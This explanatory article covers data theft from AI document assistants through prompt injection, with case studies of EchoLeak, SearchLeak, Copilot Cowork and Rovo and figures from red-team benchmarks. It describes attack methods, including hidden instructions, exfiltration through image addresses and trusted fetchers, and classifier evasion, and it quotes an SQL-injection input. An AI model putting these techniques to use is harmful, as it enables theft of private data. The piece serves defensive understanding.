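# Protecting AI systems that handle personal and company documents from data theft

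## How AI systems that read documents work, and how data is stolen from them

An AI document assistant answers questions about files, emails and other records by finding the relevant ones and passing their text to a large language model, a program that has learned from a very large body of writing to continue the text it receives. Companies use these assistants to compare contracts, summarise correspondence and look up figures. Some assistants also work as *agents*, which are AI models that can use tools, such as search, email or a command line, to carry out a task in several steps. Assistants and agents are more useful when they can read more, so organisations connect them to mailboxes, contract archives and customer records. Attackers have begun to target them as a way to reach that data. Security engineers call this kind of theft *exfiltration*, which means moving data out of a system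 to someone not entitled to it.

Microsoft 365 Copilot, which works inside Word, Outlook, Teams and Microsoft's other office programs, had more than 20 million paying users by April 2026, up from 15 million in January, according to The Decoder's *Microsoft CEO Satya Nadella says AI success is "more about getting intense users..."* Microsoft released no new total in October, but said daily users had grown more than fivefold in a year (Millward, 2026, *Microsoft Q1 Earnings*). Mint's *Microsoft posts blockbuster quarterly results riding on AI boom* reports over 50 million agents on Agent 365, Microsoft's system for managing them, 30% more than a quarter earlier. Microsoft, which sells these products, announced the figures to investors. They don't measure how much data each user or agent can reach, which matters more for security.

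### One request, step by step

Suppose a procurement officer gives such an assistant a PDF that arrived by email and types, "Compare this supplier's offer with our existing contracts."

The request goes first to an orchestrator, the conventional software that runs the steps around the model, which has to find the contracts. In Copilot, it searches through Microsoft Graph, an interface to the organisation's emails, chats, meetings and documents. It uses an index that matches on meaning as well as wording, so a search for contracts can also find a "framework agreement". Microsoft calls this step grounding. The search covers only what the officer could open herself, because Microsoft limits Copilot to the signed-in user's permissions. This limit does protect data, but only as well as the permissions themselves do. If somebody shared the finance department's folders with the whole company in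 2019, the assistant can read them on her behalf and may turn up things she would never have looked for. Microsoft offers separate tools for cleaning up such oversharing.

Next, the orchestrator assembles the text for the model. Practical 365's *Deep Dive into Copilot for Microsoft 365* describes a retrieval engine that adds its results to the user's prompt behind the scenes. The full text typically holds the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the conversation so far, passages from the contracts, the supplier's offer and the officer's eight-word request. It runs to pages, and people other than the officer wrote most of it. A language model keeps no memory between calls, so the software sends all of this again at every turn.

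The model may now output the comparison or a request for more information, such as the price schedule from 2024. It cannot open files itself, so it writes a tool call, which is a line of text in an agreed format that names a tool and what to look for. The orchestrator runs the tool and adds the result to the text for the next round. Zenity Labs, a security research group, points out that Copilot can query its data sources several times, depending on the prompt and on what earlier queries returned. Text that the assistant has already read can therefore influence what it fetches next.

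Tools also reach outside the organisation. A *connector* is a link that lets an AI system read from or act in another service, such as a mailbox or file store. Microsoft warns customers that data may leave its service boundary through plugins and web search. In Microsoft's example, a user writes that the company is considering buying a firm called Fabrikam and asks for a financial summary. Copilot sends the search engine Bing only "Fabrikam strategy" and "Fabrikam financials", and Microsoft removes the customer's identity. Very little information leaves the service in this example, but the model generates the wording of what is sent.

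Before the answer appears, Microsoft runs any further retrieval, carries out safety and compliance checks, and generates commands for the application. The officer then sees her comparison, with links to the source documents. Afterwards Microsoft keeps the prompt, response and citations as a history that administrators can search, and the orchestrator logs the interaction for auditing. An *audit log* records who or what read, changed or sent which data, and when. After a theft, investigators depend on it to establish what was taken. The history is also a new store of sensitive text, and it includes the plan to buy Fabrikam even though that plan was never sent to Bing.

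### Why a model has no firm boundary between data and instructions

Now suppose the supplier's PDF contains an instruction, in white text on a white background, to look up what rival suppliers charge. This is *prompt injection*, which means placing text where a model will read it so that the model follows the attacker's instructions instead of its user's. Simon Willison, a software developer, coined the term in 2022. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), he explains that he named it after SQL injection, an old attack on databases, because both come from mixing trusted and untrusted text. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, the centre's technical director for platforms research, David C, argues that the comparison is dangerous. He accepts that the two attacks look alike, but worries that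 engineers who see the likeness will expect the same fix to work.

Programs use the language SQL to query databases. In an SQL injection attack, a visitor to a website types text that the database engine runs as part of an instruction. This is possible when the website builds its query by pasting the visitor's text into a template. A search for Acme becomes `SELECT * FROM contracts WHERE supplier = 'Acme'`. If the visitor instead types `x' OR '1'='1`, the condition is true for every row, and the database returns the whole table. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, in which the program sends the template with a placeholder, `WHERE supplier = ?`, and sends the visitor's text separately. The engine fixes the instruction before it uses the visitor's text, so the text cannot change it. The engine searches for a supplier named `x' OR '1'='1` and finds none.

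A language model has no such placeholder. It receives one sequence of tokens (words and fragments of words) and calculates a likely next token, then another. As David C puts it, "there is only ever 'next token'". The system prompt, the officer's request, the contracts and the supplier's hidden sentence are all in that sequence, and the model processes them all with the same calculation.

Developers can put markers around the supplier's text, train the model to give commands inside it less weight, or run a detector over it first. These measures make attacks harder but can't rule them out, because the technology has no built-in distinction between instructions and data. Filters for known bad phrases are the weakest, since an attacker can keep rewording. Willison gives an example from August 2025, in which a planted support ticket was used to attack the programming tool Cursor. Models often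 refuse to steal *access tokens*, the digital credentials that let one program use another service without a password. So the ticket asked for a "rotten apple" in the code, a long string starting with "eyJ", as a common type of token does.

David C prefers another comparison, the *confused deputy*, which is a privileged program that a less privileged person manipulates into using its privileges for him. This fits the procurement case well, because the supplier cannot open his rivals' contracts but has given something to read to an assistant that can. Engineers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but David C calls language models "inherently confusable" and expects the risk to remain.

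He offers no proof and says only that prompt injection "may never be totally mitigated". His argument also covers only the model. If ordinary code around the model blocks all outgoing email, no email goes out, whatever the model produces. He therefore advises designers to assume that anyone who gets text in front of the model can do whatever its tools can do, to limit those tools with deterministic code, and to log enough to notice an attacker's early failures. If the remaining risk is still intolerable, a language model may be unsuitable for the job. He is uneasy because of the history of SQL injection. Researchers described it in the 1990s, but websites adopted SQL without precautions anyway, and attacks peaked only around 2010.

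### The lethal trifecta

To steal data through a hidden instruction, an attacker needs the model to follow it and the data to leave the system. Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out the *lethal trifecta*, and claims that an attacker can easily steal data from any system with all three. The procurement request supplies the first two, because the contracts are private and an outsider wrote the offer.

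Data can leave through pictures, an easily overlooked route, because an assistant with no email tool or web browser may still display them. Suppose the hidden text contains an instruction to end the answer with a small logo from the supplier's web server and to add the rivals' prices to the logo's address. The officer sees a logo, which her computer loads automatically, without a click. Loading it sends the prices to the supplier's server, which records every address requested.

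In January 2026, Willison described a flaw in Superhuman AI, an email assistant. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, a planted message caused the assistant to submit the contents of dozens of other messages, including financial, legal and medical ones, to an attacker's Google Form. Superhuman had an *allowlist*, which blocks requests to any address not on it. The list included docs.google.com so that images could load, but a Google Form at that address stores whatever data a request carries. Superhuman fixed the flaw.

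Attackers can also steal data through a much more restricted channel. The web-reading tool in Claude, Anthropic's AI assistant, could open only addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned, and links on pages it had already opened. Willison described in July 2026 how Ayush Paul exploited those links. Paul built a site with pages for each letter of the alphabet and told visiting AI assistants to reach the user's profile by following links that spelled out the user's details. From the sequence of page requests, he learned the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on pages it had opened.

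Willison recommends removing one of the three ingredients and finds that the means of sending data out is generally the easiest to remove. Without either of the other two, the assistant often can't do its task. David C relays a simple rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. This works well for an assistant that sorts mail from strangers. But if the rule were applied literally to the procurement request, an assistant that had read the supplier's offer would no longer be allowed to read the contracts it has to compare it with.

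Researchers can easily use these methods, but it is much less clear how often criminals do. Willison has collected dozens of examples, most of them from researchers whose reports led the vendor to fix the problem. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* (April 2026) reports that the security company Forcepoint found ten sets of planted instructions on live web pages. One only instructed AI systems to credit a certain consultant. Others were requests for a secret key or full directions for making a $5,000 PayPal payment. Forcepoint sells protection against such attacks, and its findings don't show how many victims these attempts had.

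### Three routes to the data

Prompt injection works through the model and uses the assistant's own permissions, which makes it hard to spot afterwards. Anthropic notes in *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) that once a poisoned tool result has steered an agent into sending data away, the log shows only a successful, authorised request. The planted text can also arrive through the user. In an internal exercise in February 2026, a researcher at the company emailed an employee a ready-made prompt to run in Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. Among routine setup steps, the prompt included an instruction to read a file of cloud credentials and send the contents to an outside address. The agent did so in 24 of 25 runs. Defences in the model look for departures from what the user wants, but here the user had entered the request.

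An intruder can also bypass the model and break into the data store behind it. This is conventional hacking, through an interface left open or through SQL injection, and even a model that resisted every hidden instruction would not stop it. The assistant concentrates data in one place, because answering questions across a whole organisation requires a searchable index of documents that used to be stored separately. It also builds up a history of what staff have asked. The intruder may itself be an AI agent, as in the break-in at Lilli, the internal assistant of the consulting firm McKinsey. An intruder who can write to the store as well as read it can also plant instructions there. Anthropic warns about planted instructions in the memory that an agent carries from one session to the next, because the agent reloads them every time it starts.

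The remaining route is through a connected supplier. A company that links an outside service to its customer database gives the service an access token, and a thief who steals the token from the supplier can query the database by posing as the supplier's software. This happened in the Salesloft Drift thefts. The customer's passwords and sign-in checks don't stop the thief, because the token stands for a sign-in that has already taken place. Vetting the supplier at the start gives limited protection because, as Anthropic points out, a remote tool can change its behaviour at any time after the customer has approved it.

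One attack can use more than one route. The employee in Anthropic's exercise lost credentials through the model, and a real thief could then have used them directly, without an AI system. Agents can also disclose data without an attacker, because a model sometimes takes a harmful step that nobody asked for.

### The chance of success and what it can reach

Better models should make theft through the model rarer. Whether they make it cheaper for the victim is a separate matter, because the damage depends on two quantities:

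expected loss per attack = chance that the attack succeeds × what a successful attack can reach

An AI model that resists attacks better can still lose more data if it is connected to more files. In a hypothetical example, a company's older assistant reads a team folder of 200 files, and 1% of attacks on it succeed, exposing 2 files per attack on average. Only 0.1% of attacks on its successor succeed, so the company connects it to 200,000 files, and each attack now exposes 200 on average. The expected loss per attack rose a hundredfold because the number of files grew by a factor of 1,000 while the chance of success fell by a factor of ten. The newer assistant's risk is also harder to judge from experience, because it will very probably get through its first hundred attacks without losing any files.

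This calculation is crude. It treats every file as equally valuable and assumes that a successful attacker takes everything within reach, so the result is an upper bound for a single attempt. Stealing 200,000 files with Paul's alphabet of web pages, for example, would take a very long time. But the calculation also understates the risk, because attackers can try again. The *attack success rate*, here the share of attempts on which the attacker gets what he wants, was roughly 0.1% for Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.7 on single attempts in one benchmark, but 5 to 6% after a hundred adaptive ones. At 5%, the second invented assistant exposes 10,000 files on average per determined attacker. Wider adoption also adds targets, since an attacker can send the same planted text to any number of organisations.

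Anthropic wrote in May 2026 that progress on safeguards and training has steadily reduced the likelihood of failure, while the theoretical *blast radius* "only grows as capabilities and access expand". Blast radius here means the most damage that one successful attack or failure could do, given what the system can reach. As evidence, the company says that a year earlier it would have refused outright to give Claude enough access to take down an internal service, but by May its developers routinely gave it that access. This is one company's experience, and it doesn't include a figure for the blast radius, so readers can't use it to check whether the likelihood of failure multiplied by the blast radius has risen. Still, the blast radius plausibly grows as failures become rarer, because people hand more work to a system that fails less often, and more work usually needs more access.

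Anthropic also points out that designers can limit the damage an attack can do, known as its "blast radius". If the second hypothetical assistant could read only the 500 contracts that the procurement team uses, the expected loss per attack would drop to half a file, with no change to the model. Designers can also keep credentials out of the agent's environment or use *egress controls*, which limit the network connections that a system may open to the outside. Another option is *information-flow control*, which labels data by source and permitted readers and checks the labels before each action. Asking the user to approve each step has proved a poor substitute for these measures. Users of Claude Code approved roughly 93% of the requests they saw and paid less attention as the number of requests grew.

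Caps on access make an assistant less useful, because one confined to 500 contracts cannot answer a question about the 501st. Sometimes a developer also decides that caps are not enough. Anthropic judged the potential damage from one model, Claude Mythos Preview, too great to release it in April 2026. Caps are also software, so they can fail if they are badly written. Anthropic reports that the established isolation tools it adopted from elsewhere have been dependable, but that a network filter it built itself failed.

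## EchoLeak: an email that could make Microsoft 365 Copilot leak files

In June 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, described EchoLeak, a way to steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending an employee one email. Researchers call this a zero-click attack because the employee did not have to open the email or click on anything. She did have to later ask Copilot about a subject that the email appeared to cover. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, explains how the attack got past a detector for planted instructions, a filter on links and a limit on where the browser may load images from.

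### Getting the email in front of the model

Copilot searches the user's mailbox, so anyone who knows an employee's address can add text to the search by sending an email. The text has no effect until a search retrieves it, and an outsider can't know what the employee will ask. Search systems of this kind typically convert each passage into a list of numbers that represents its meaning, then retrieve the passages whose numbers are closest to those of the question. A short email would be retrieved only for questions about its subject. Aim Labs therefore wrote a long one, assuming that Copilot would split it into chunks, and presented each part as a guide to a different office matter, such as onboarding new staff or taking leave. Every part contained the same instructions.

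The team also considered a subtler method. They reasoned that swapping a few letters for similar-looking characters barely affects how a language model reads a text but can greatly change the numbers that represent it, so an attacker could spread many altered copies across the index. They confirmed the change in the numbers on an OpenAI system. They couldn't tune the method to Copilot because Microsoft doesn't publish which system Copilot uses, and the office headings worked well enough without it. Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics but doesn't say how often, so it is hard to say how long a real attacker would have had to wait.

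The first defence was a classifier, a program that Microsoft had trained to recognise planted instructions and keep them away from the model. Aim Labs got past it by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning Copilot, assistants or AI, so the email read like an ordinary request to a colleague. A stricter classifier would presumably have caught it, but would also have blocked a good deal of legitimate email. Ravia adds that developers lack good collections of real attacks to train classifiers on.

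The email was now in the model's context alongside internal files. Copilot's permission check did not prevent this, because the employee was allowed to read both. The email contained instructions to pick out the most sensitive information in the context, which could include the chat history and anything Copilot had fetched for the question. Ravia describes no defence at this point and proposes the name "LLM scope violation" for what happened, meaning that text from an untrusted source directs the model to trusted data. Willison (2025), commenting on the report, doubts that the pattern is new or needs a name and considers it ordinary prompt injection.

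### Getting the data out

Copilot then had to put the stolen text into a web address on the attacker's server, as in the example of the supplier's logo.

Microsoft had anticipated this and used a filter to remove links to outside sites before the user saw them. Copilot writes its answers in Markdown, a simple notation for formatted text. A link's address in Markdown can go right beside the words to click on or on a separate line, like a footnote. The filter missed links written in the footnote form, so an attacker could steal data from a user who clicked one. Aim Labs then found that the filter also missed images written in the footnote form, so the attack no longer needed a click.

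The remaining obstacle was the *content security policy*, a list of the sources from which a web page may load images and other material. The website sends the list with the page and the browser enforces it, so the wording of an email has no effect on it. The attacker's server wasn't on Copilot's list, so the browser refused to load the image.

However, the list had about thirty entries, nearly all of them Microsoft's own, and some covered every site under a domain. Aim Labs searched them for a service that would fetch a page from another site on request. SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, could do this, but only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Microsoft Teams could do it without an invitation. The browser asked Teams for the image, as the policy allowed. A Teams server then requested the attacker's address, which contained the stolen text.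 The policy didn't block this second request because it covers only requests from the browser. The attacker could then read the text in his server's log.

Copilot normally cites its sources, which might have led the employee to the email. To prevent this, Aim Labs added a line telling the recipient never to refer to the email, supposedly for compliance reasons.

The classifier failed at a judgement that is hard to make reliably. The link filter and the content security policy are ordinary code, and they failed because their rules were incomplete. Microsoft could fix both faults exactly, but each fix would cover only the case somebody had noticed.

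### The repair, and whether anyone used the flaw

Aim Labs reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on public material, dates the first repairs to April and the full repair to May. Microsoft made the change on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. It published the flaw on 11 June as CVE-2025-32711, a number in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. The case study also mentions recent changes that strip footnote-style links and embedded images from outside text. According to SOC Prime's *CVE-2025-32711 Vulnerability*, administrators can also stop Copilot from processing external emails, though this makes Copilot less useful.

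Microsoft rated EchoLeak's severity at 9.3 out of 10. The US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5 (GCVE, 2025). Both scores are for an attack over the network that needs no account and no action by the victim. Microsoft's score is higher because it also counted some ability to alter data and an effect beyond the vulnerable component.

There is no public evidence that criminals used EchoLeak. Microsoft told Aim Labs that no customers were affected, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA entered "Exploitation: none" in the vulnerability's record three days after disclosure. These statements probably rest on Microsoft's own logs. A victim would have had little to report, because a successful theft looked like a broken image on her screen.

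A month later, Microsoft (2025) described its defences in *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks*. It separates probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. Blocking theft through images is a deterministic defence. Microsoft added that when researchers report a flaw, it protects against "the general class of issues, including variants". The following year's findings are a fair test of that claim.

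### SearchLeak: another trusted address

In June 2026 the data-security company Varonis published *SearchLeak*, which describes a second way to steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot through an image. The victim only has to click a link. The link opens Copilot's search page at Microsoft's genuine address, so tools that check links for fraud are unlikely to block it. The address can include a search query, which Copilot treated as a prompt and carried out immediately.

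The prompt in Varonis's demonstration made Copilot search the victim's mailbox, take the title of an email and put it in the address of an image. Titles can be worth stealing because many services put one-time login codes in them. Varonis adds that an attacker could have reached calendars and company files in the same way. SearchLeak went further than EchoLeak by making Copilot run a search. EchoLeak, as Ravia describes it, took data that was already in the model's context.

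Microsoft defended against images in Copilot's output by wrapping each answer in a code block, which makes the browser display any image command as plain text. But it added the code block only after Copilot had finished the answer. The browser displays an answer while the model is still producing it, so it had already requested the image by then.

The content security policy should still have stopped the request, but its list of allowed sites included Microsoft's Bing, whose image search fetches images from any address it is given. SearchLeak used Bing to get around the policy, as EchoLeak had used Teams. Bing was also on the list that Ravia printed in 2025, so anyone checking that list for services that fetch outside addresses could have found this route a year earlier.

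Fixing EchoLeak removed one instance of this fault but left another in place. The fix was still useful, because Varonis had to find a new way in and a gap in the timing of the output filter. Its attack also needed a click, unlike EchoLeak.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), published on 4 June, records the flaw as critical, fully mitigated and not exploited, with a score of 6.5. Microsoft gave EchoLeak a much higher score, 9.3, partly because it also counted tampering and a wider effect. The 7.5 that the US database gave EchoLeak is a fairer comparison with the 6.5, because those two assessments differ only in whether the attack needs the user to click.

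### Copilot Cowork: a message to oneself

Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent, offered in a preview programme, that can send email, post in Teams and reorganise files with the user's own permissions. In May 2026 the security company PromptArmor showed in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* how an attacker could use it to obtain whole files. The attack begins with a *skill*, a file of instructions that teaches the agent a task. Employees often find such files online and upload them. Five of the 81 lines in PromptArmor's skill were the attacker's.

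When the user asked for a review of her week, the agent loaded the skill and collected download links for her recent documents. Microsoft's storage services can issue links that let anyone who has them download the file without signing in. The agent then sent the user a Teams message containing images whose addresses included those links. When she opened the message, Teams loaded the images, which sent the links to the attacker.

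According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams. PromptArmor found that it doesn't ask when the recipient is the user herself, and that users can't change this. Even a message to oneself can leak data outside the organisation if it displays external images. The content security policy on Copilot's own page doesn't prevent this, because the images load in Teams or Outlook.

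The attack worked in all five trials. PromptArmor ran it first with automatic model selection, which switched between two of Anthropic's models, and then with only the more advanced of the two, Claude Opus 4.7. The same five lines worked again, and Opus 4.7 leaked more because it searched more thoroughly for recent documents and included every file from that week's earlier Cowork sessions. The test was small, used one planted text, and was run by a company that sells protection against such attacks, but it is a concrete case of a more capable model increasing the damage. The thoroughness that helps the model write a better weekly review also led it to leak more files.

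PromptArmor describes the problem as a design risk rather than a bug, and it suggests ways for administrators to limit the damage but reports no fix. Microsoft did fix a different flaw in the same product. The agent runs its code in a sandbox, an isolated environment that is supposed to have no internet access. According to PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* (2026), malicious code in a skill could make a file-copying service outside the sandbox request any address the attacker chose. Like Teams and Bing before it, this was a trusted service that fetched any address it received. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had mitigated it.

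### Rovo: the same weakness at another company

The problem also affects Rovo, Atlassian's AI assistant. Rovo works across Jira, which companies use to track tasks, and Confluence, which they use for internal documents. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, published in August 2026, describes a user who uploads a guide she found online and asks Rovo to organise her Jira tickets. Hidden text in the guide makes Rovo append tickets and documents to a web address on the attacker's server and then open that address.

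This attack uses Rovo's tool for opening web pages, so it needs no image or browser. PromptArmor found nothing to stop the tool from opening an address that the model had just composed. The attack worked even when an organisation had switched off web search for Rovo, because that setting left the page-opening tool in place. Rovo also displays images from the model's output, which gives an attacker a second way to send data out.

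The attack only requires the model to read a malicious file and write a tool call, so nothing has to execute the file. An article on Atlassian's community site, *Can Rovo Be Tricked by Malicious Files?*, doesn't account for this. It gives the short answer "No", arguing that Rovo is an interface around the model that filters files and applies Atlassian's security controls before any text reaches the model, and that Rovo doesn't execute what a file contains.

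PromptArmor reported the flaw on 23 May and received thanks and a case number two days later. It followed up twice, heard nothing more, and published on 5 August while the flaw was still open. The Hacker News (2026) reported later that month that customers had no patch to apply and could only limit which apps and groups use Rovo. Atlassian was quicker to fix a flaw that Varonis had found, in which a link could load an attacker's prompt into Rovo's chat, much as in SearchLeak. It fixed that flaw on its own servers on 8 July.

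### Which defences would have worked

Reddy and Gujral propose a long list of defences and rate eight of them against six elements of the EchoLeak attack in a table of ticks and crosses. They say a tick means full coverage "in our tests", but they also state that they ran no experiments, and they call the table theoretical in its caption. The table is best read as a set of expectations that can be checked against the later attacks.

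They first suggest a hard separation between trusted and untrusted text, made by marking outside text with tags and instructing the model not to obey anything inside them. This separation is much weaker than "hard" implies, because it depends on the model following that instruction. Microsoft's version, Spotlighting, can also insert a special character between all the words of an outside text or encode the whole text. Microsoft classes Spotlighting as a probabilistic defense. It would probably have done nothing against SearchLeak, because the attacker's words arrived where the user's own request belongs.

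A stronger proposal is to exclude outside material from answers about internal matters unless the user asks for it. Reddy and Gujral write that EchoLeak then "fails by design", yet their table marks this defence as failing against zero-click theft. The text is more convincing, because an email that never reaches the model can't direct it. However, none of the later attacks depended on an unsolicited email. The victims clicked a link, installed a skill or uploaded a guide, and an assistant would have good reason to treat all of these as requests from the user.

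Reddy and Gujral expect controls on outgoing data to help most, including a strict content security policy that allows only the site's own addresses, with no wildcards. But Teams and Bing are Microsoft's own addresses, so an administrator could follow that advice carefully and still let both attacks through. A more useful test, from Varonis, is whether an approved domain will fetch an address that a user supplies. Reddy and Gujral also advise removing query parameters, the extra values at the end of a web address, from links to approved sites. Teams and Bing both received the attacker's address as a parameter, so this would have blocked both routes if Microsoft had applied it to images too. Some legitimate images would also have stopped loading.

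They also advise checking the model's output before anything displays it. SearchLeak supports this advice, because Microsoft's check was sound but ran too late.

However, a content security policy protects only one web page, so it did not cover Cowork's messages in Teams or Rovo's page-opening tool. Reddy and Gujral also recommend limiting what the servers may request. Rovo, for example, could open only addresses that the user has typed or a search has returned. Claude's web tool had a similar rule, but Ayush Paul got around it with an alphabet of web pages. Even so, a route that leaks a few words at a time is much better than one that leaks whole documents. Attackers can also abuse approved addresses without using images, as happened with Anthropic's Claude Cowork.

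The table lists human approval as a defence against zero-click theft, but how well it works depends on the implementation. Cowork required approval for messages to other people, but not for the kind of message the attack needed. Requiring it for those messages too might not have helped much, because PromptArmor found that Cowork's activity view never displayed the malicious content, even when the user clicked on the action.

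All of these measures are meant to stop the theft. Reddy and Gujral also recommend narrowing the AI system's access to data, which would have reduced the loss in every attack described here. Microsoft's research project FIDES uses information-flow control, a finer-grained approach.

For administrators who can't wait for that, PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) recommends reviewing old sharing permissions and excluding sensitive sites from Copilot's search. It also recommends blocking downloads from chosen sites, so that the agent can't obtain the links that the Cowork attack stole. Employees then can't download or print files from those sites or open them in Word and Excel. Copilot can still read the files, so an attacker could still have it copy text from them into an image's address.

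## Red-team tests: do more capable models resist hidden instructions?

The attacks on Copilot and Rovo all relied on a model following instructions written by an attacker. If models reliably ignored such instructions, the gaps in Microsoft's filters and lists of approved sites would matter much less. Developers use red-team tests to measure how well models resist them. In these tests, people or programs attack a system with its owner's consent and record how often the attacks succeed.

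### How a test is built

*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a three-week public competition run by Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems for their developers. In each of the 41 scenarios, an agent had an ordinary task, and the attacker could write text in one place to try to make it take a specified harmful action. Each scenario also had a rule for deciding whether the attack had worked. In one scenario, the user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails, and the attacker controls the text of a marketing email in the inbox. The attack succeeds if the assistant marks a message about a contract deadline as read and leaves it out of the summary.

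A program checked whether the agent had taken the harmful action. In most scenarios a language model also graded the agent's final answer, and the attack counted as failed if the answer revealed it. Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, but the attack stayed hidden in only about half of those, so its official rate was 8.5%. Requiring the attack to stay hidden makes sense for the missed deadline, because a user who notices can still act. But it understates the danger of data theft, because the files have already been stolen by the time the user finds out.

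Contestants could see the whole conversation, knew which action to aim for and could retry immediately. A real thief usually has none of these advantages, so Dziemian and colleagues treat their results as an upper bound for attacks that get one turn with the agent. But the bound holds only for attackers about as skilled and persistent as the contestants.

The 464 contestants made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models, and roughly 3% succeeded. Attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded least often, at 0.5%, but at least one succeeded in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the final results. A success rate is therefore hard to interpret without knowing whether it counts attempts or scenarios.

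### One attempt and a hundred attempts

Attacks are more likely to succeed when the attacker can try repeatedly. On the Agent Red Teaming benchmark, an older Gray Swan test, Anthropic reports a success rate against Claude Opus 4.7 of roughly 0.1% for single attempts and 5 to 6% after 100 adaptive ones. An adaptive attacker changes each new text based on how the model handled the last one.

If every attempt had the same 0.1% chance and none affected the others, the chance of at least one success in 100 would be

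1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰ ≈ 9.5%

The reported figure is lower, probably because some scenarios are much harder than others. If the attacker had no chance in 93 out of 100 scenarios and a 1-in-70 chance per attempt in each of the other seven, the average success rate per attempt would still be 0.1%. After 100 attempts in each scenario, he would probably have succeeded in most of the seven but in none of the other 93, so his overall success rate would be about 5.3%. A failed attempt is a sign that the scenario is hard, which makes a second failure in the same scenario more likely than the first.

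Adaptation has the opposite effect, since an attacker who learns from failures should be more likely to succeed on the fiftieth attempt than on the first. The published figures don't separate the two effects.

The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that attacks on this earlier model in a Gray Swan benchmark succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100. If the attempts were independent, the rates would have been about 38% with ten and 99% with 100. The first ten attempts therefore helped the attacker nearly as much as independence would predict, but the next ninety helped much less than predicted. The drop from 63% for Opus 4.5 to 5 or 6% for Opus 4.7 suggests a large improvement, but the two models may not have faced the same attacks.

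Attempts on different victims aren't independent either. Dziemian and colleagues reran successful attacks on the models they had beaten, and at least half worked again on the Claude and GPT models. An attacker who needs a thousand tries to find an email that works can then send it to every company that uses the same assistant. The attacks that are hardest to find also seem to transfer best to other models. The 44 attacks that had beaten Opus 4.5 worked on the other models 44 to 81% of the time, while none of the attacks that had beaten Qwen3, a much weaker model from Alibaba, worked on Opus 4.5.

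### Models of different capability on the same test

Dziemian and colleagues compared how often attacks on each model succeeded with the model's score on GPQA Diamond, a set of hard science questions. Higher-scoring models were slightly harder to attack, but with so few models the link could easily be chance (r = −0.31, p = 0.3). Gemini 2.5 Pro and Moonshot's Kimi K2 both scored around 85%, but attackers succeeded 8.5% of the time against Gemini and 4.8% against Kimi. How developers train their models seems to matter more than how capable the models are.

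Among models from the same developer, the more capable ones often resist hidden instructions better. In the competition, attackers succeeded on 0.5% of attempts against Claude Opus 4.5, 1.0% against the less capable Sonnet 4.5 and 1.3% against Haiku 4.5, the least capable of the three. The system card (a safety report) that Anthropic published with Claude Opus 5 in July 2026 shows the same pattern for OpenAI's models. An attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 20.0% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol, the most capable version, compared with 30.4% against Terra and 43.9% against Luna.

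Those figures come from a newer Gray Swan benchmark, which reuses attacks from its competitions. Anthropic had stopped reporting the older one because its models were at or near the best possible score, so the results no longer distinguished them. Anthropic's own models did not keep to a consistent order across the July tests:

| Model | Newer Gray Swan benchmark, within 15 attempts | Coding, share of attempts | Computer use, share of attempts | Web browser, share of attempts |
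|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% | 0.45% | 0.82% | 29.7% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | 0.56% | 0.54% | 3.70% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% | 0.31% | 2.25% | 0.93% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% | 7.03% | 7.14% | 31.5% |

All the models could reason before answering, and none had extra protection against injection. "Computer use" means the agent works from screenshots and controls a mouse and keyboard.

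Opus 5 was harder to attack than its predecessor, Opus 4.8, in every column. But Sonnet 5, from a less capable line than Opus and Mythos, was by far the hardest to attack in the browser. Mythos 5 was about thirty times easier to attack there than Sonnet 5, and almost as easy as Opus 4.8. When Anthropic released Mythos 5 in June, it described the model as broadly comparable to Opus 4.8 at resisting attacks on agents, even though Mythos 5 is more capable.

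The newest figures are from September, when Anthropic released Claude Fable 5.1. On an enlarged version of the Gray Swan benchmark, attackers succeeded against it 0.1% of the time with one attempt and 1.0% with 15. Among other companies' models, Gemini 3.7 Flash did best, at 9.2% with 15 attempts, and most were between 24% and 53%. Opus 5's rate rose from 2.0% in July to 4.8%, after Gray Swan added nine scenarios and 670 attacks and Anthropic changed the set-up so that a safety classifier passed some requests to the older Opus 4.8. A model's score in one month therefore doesn't reliably predict how it will do against the next set of attacks.

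Anthropic published these comparisons, and its own models did better than other companies' models. However, Gray Swan ran the September tests and accessed the other companies' models through their public services, which may have included extra protection. Anthropic also excluded models that contestants had attacked directly, because attacks tailored to a model make it look worse.

The ranking is hard to check against the other companies' published results. According to a VentureBeat comparison, OpenAI's system card for GPT-5.5 gave a single score against known attacks on connectors, and Google published no injection test for its Gemini 3 models. Only Anthropic showed how attackers' success rate rose with repeated attempts.

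### Training, classifiers and an attacker who adapts

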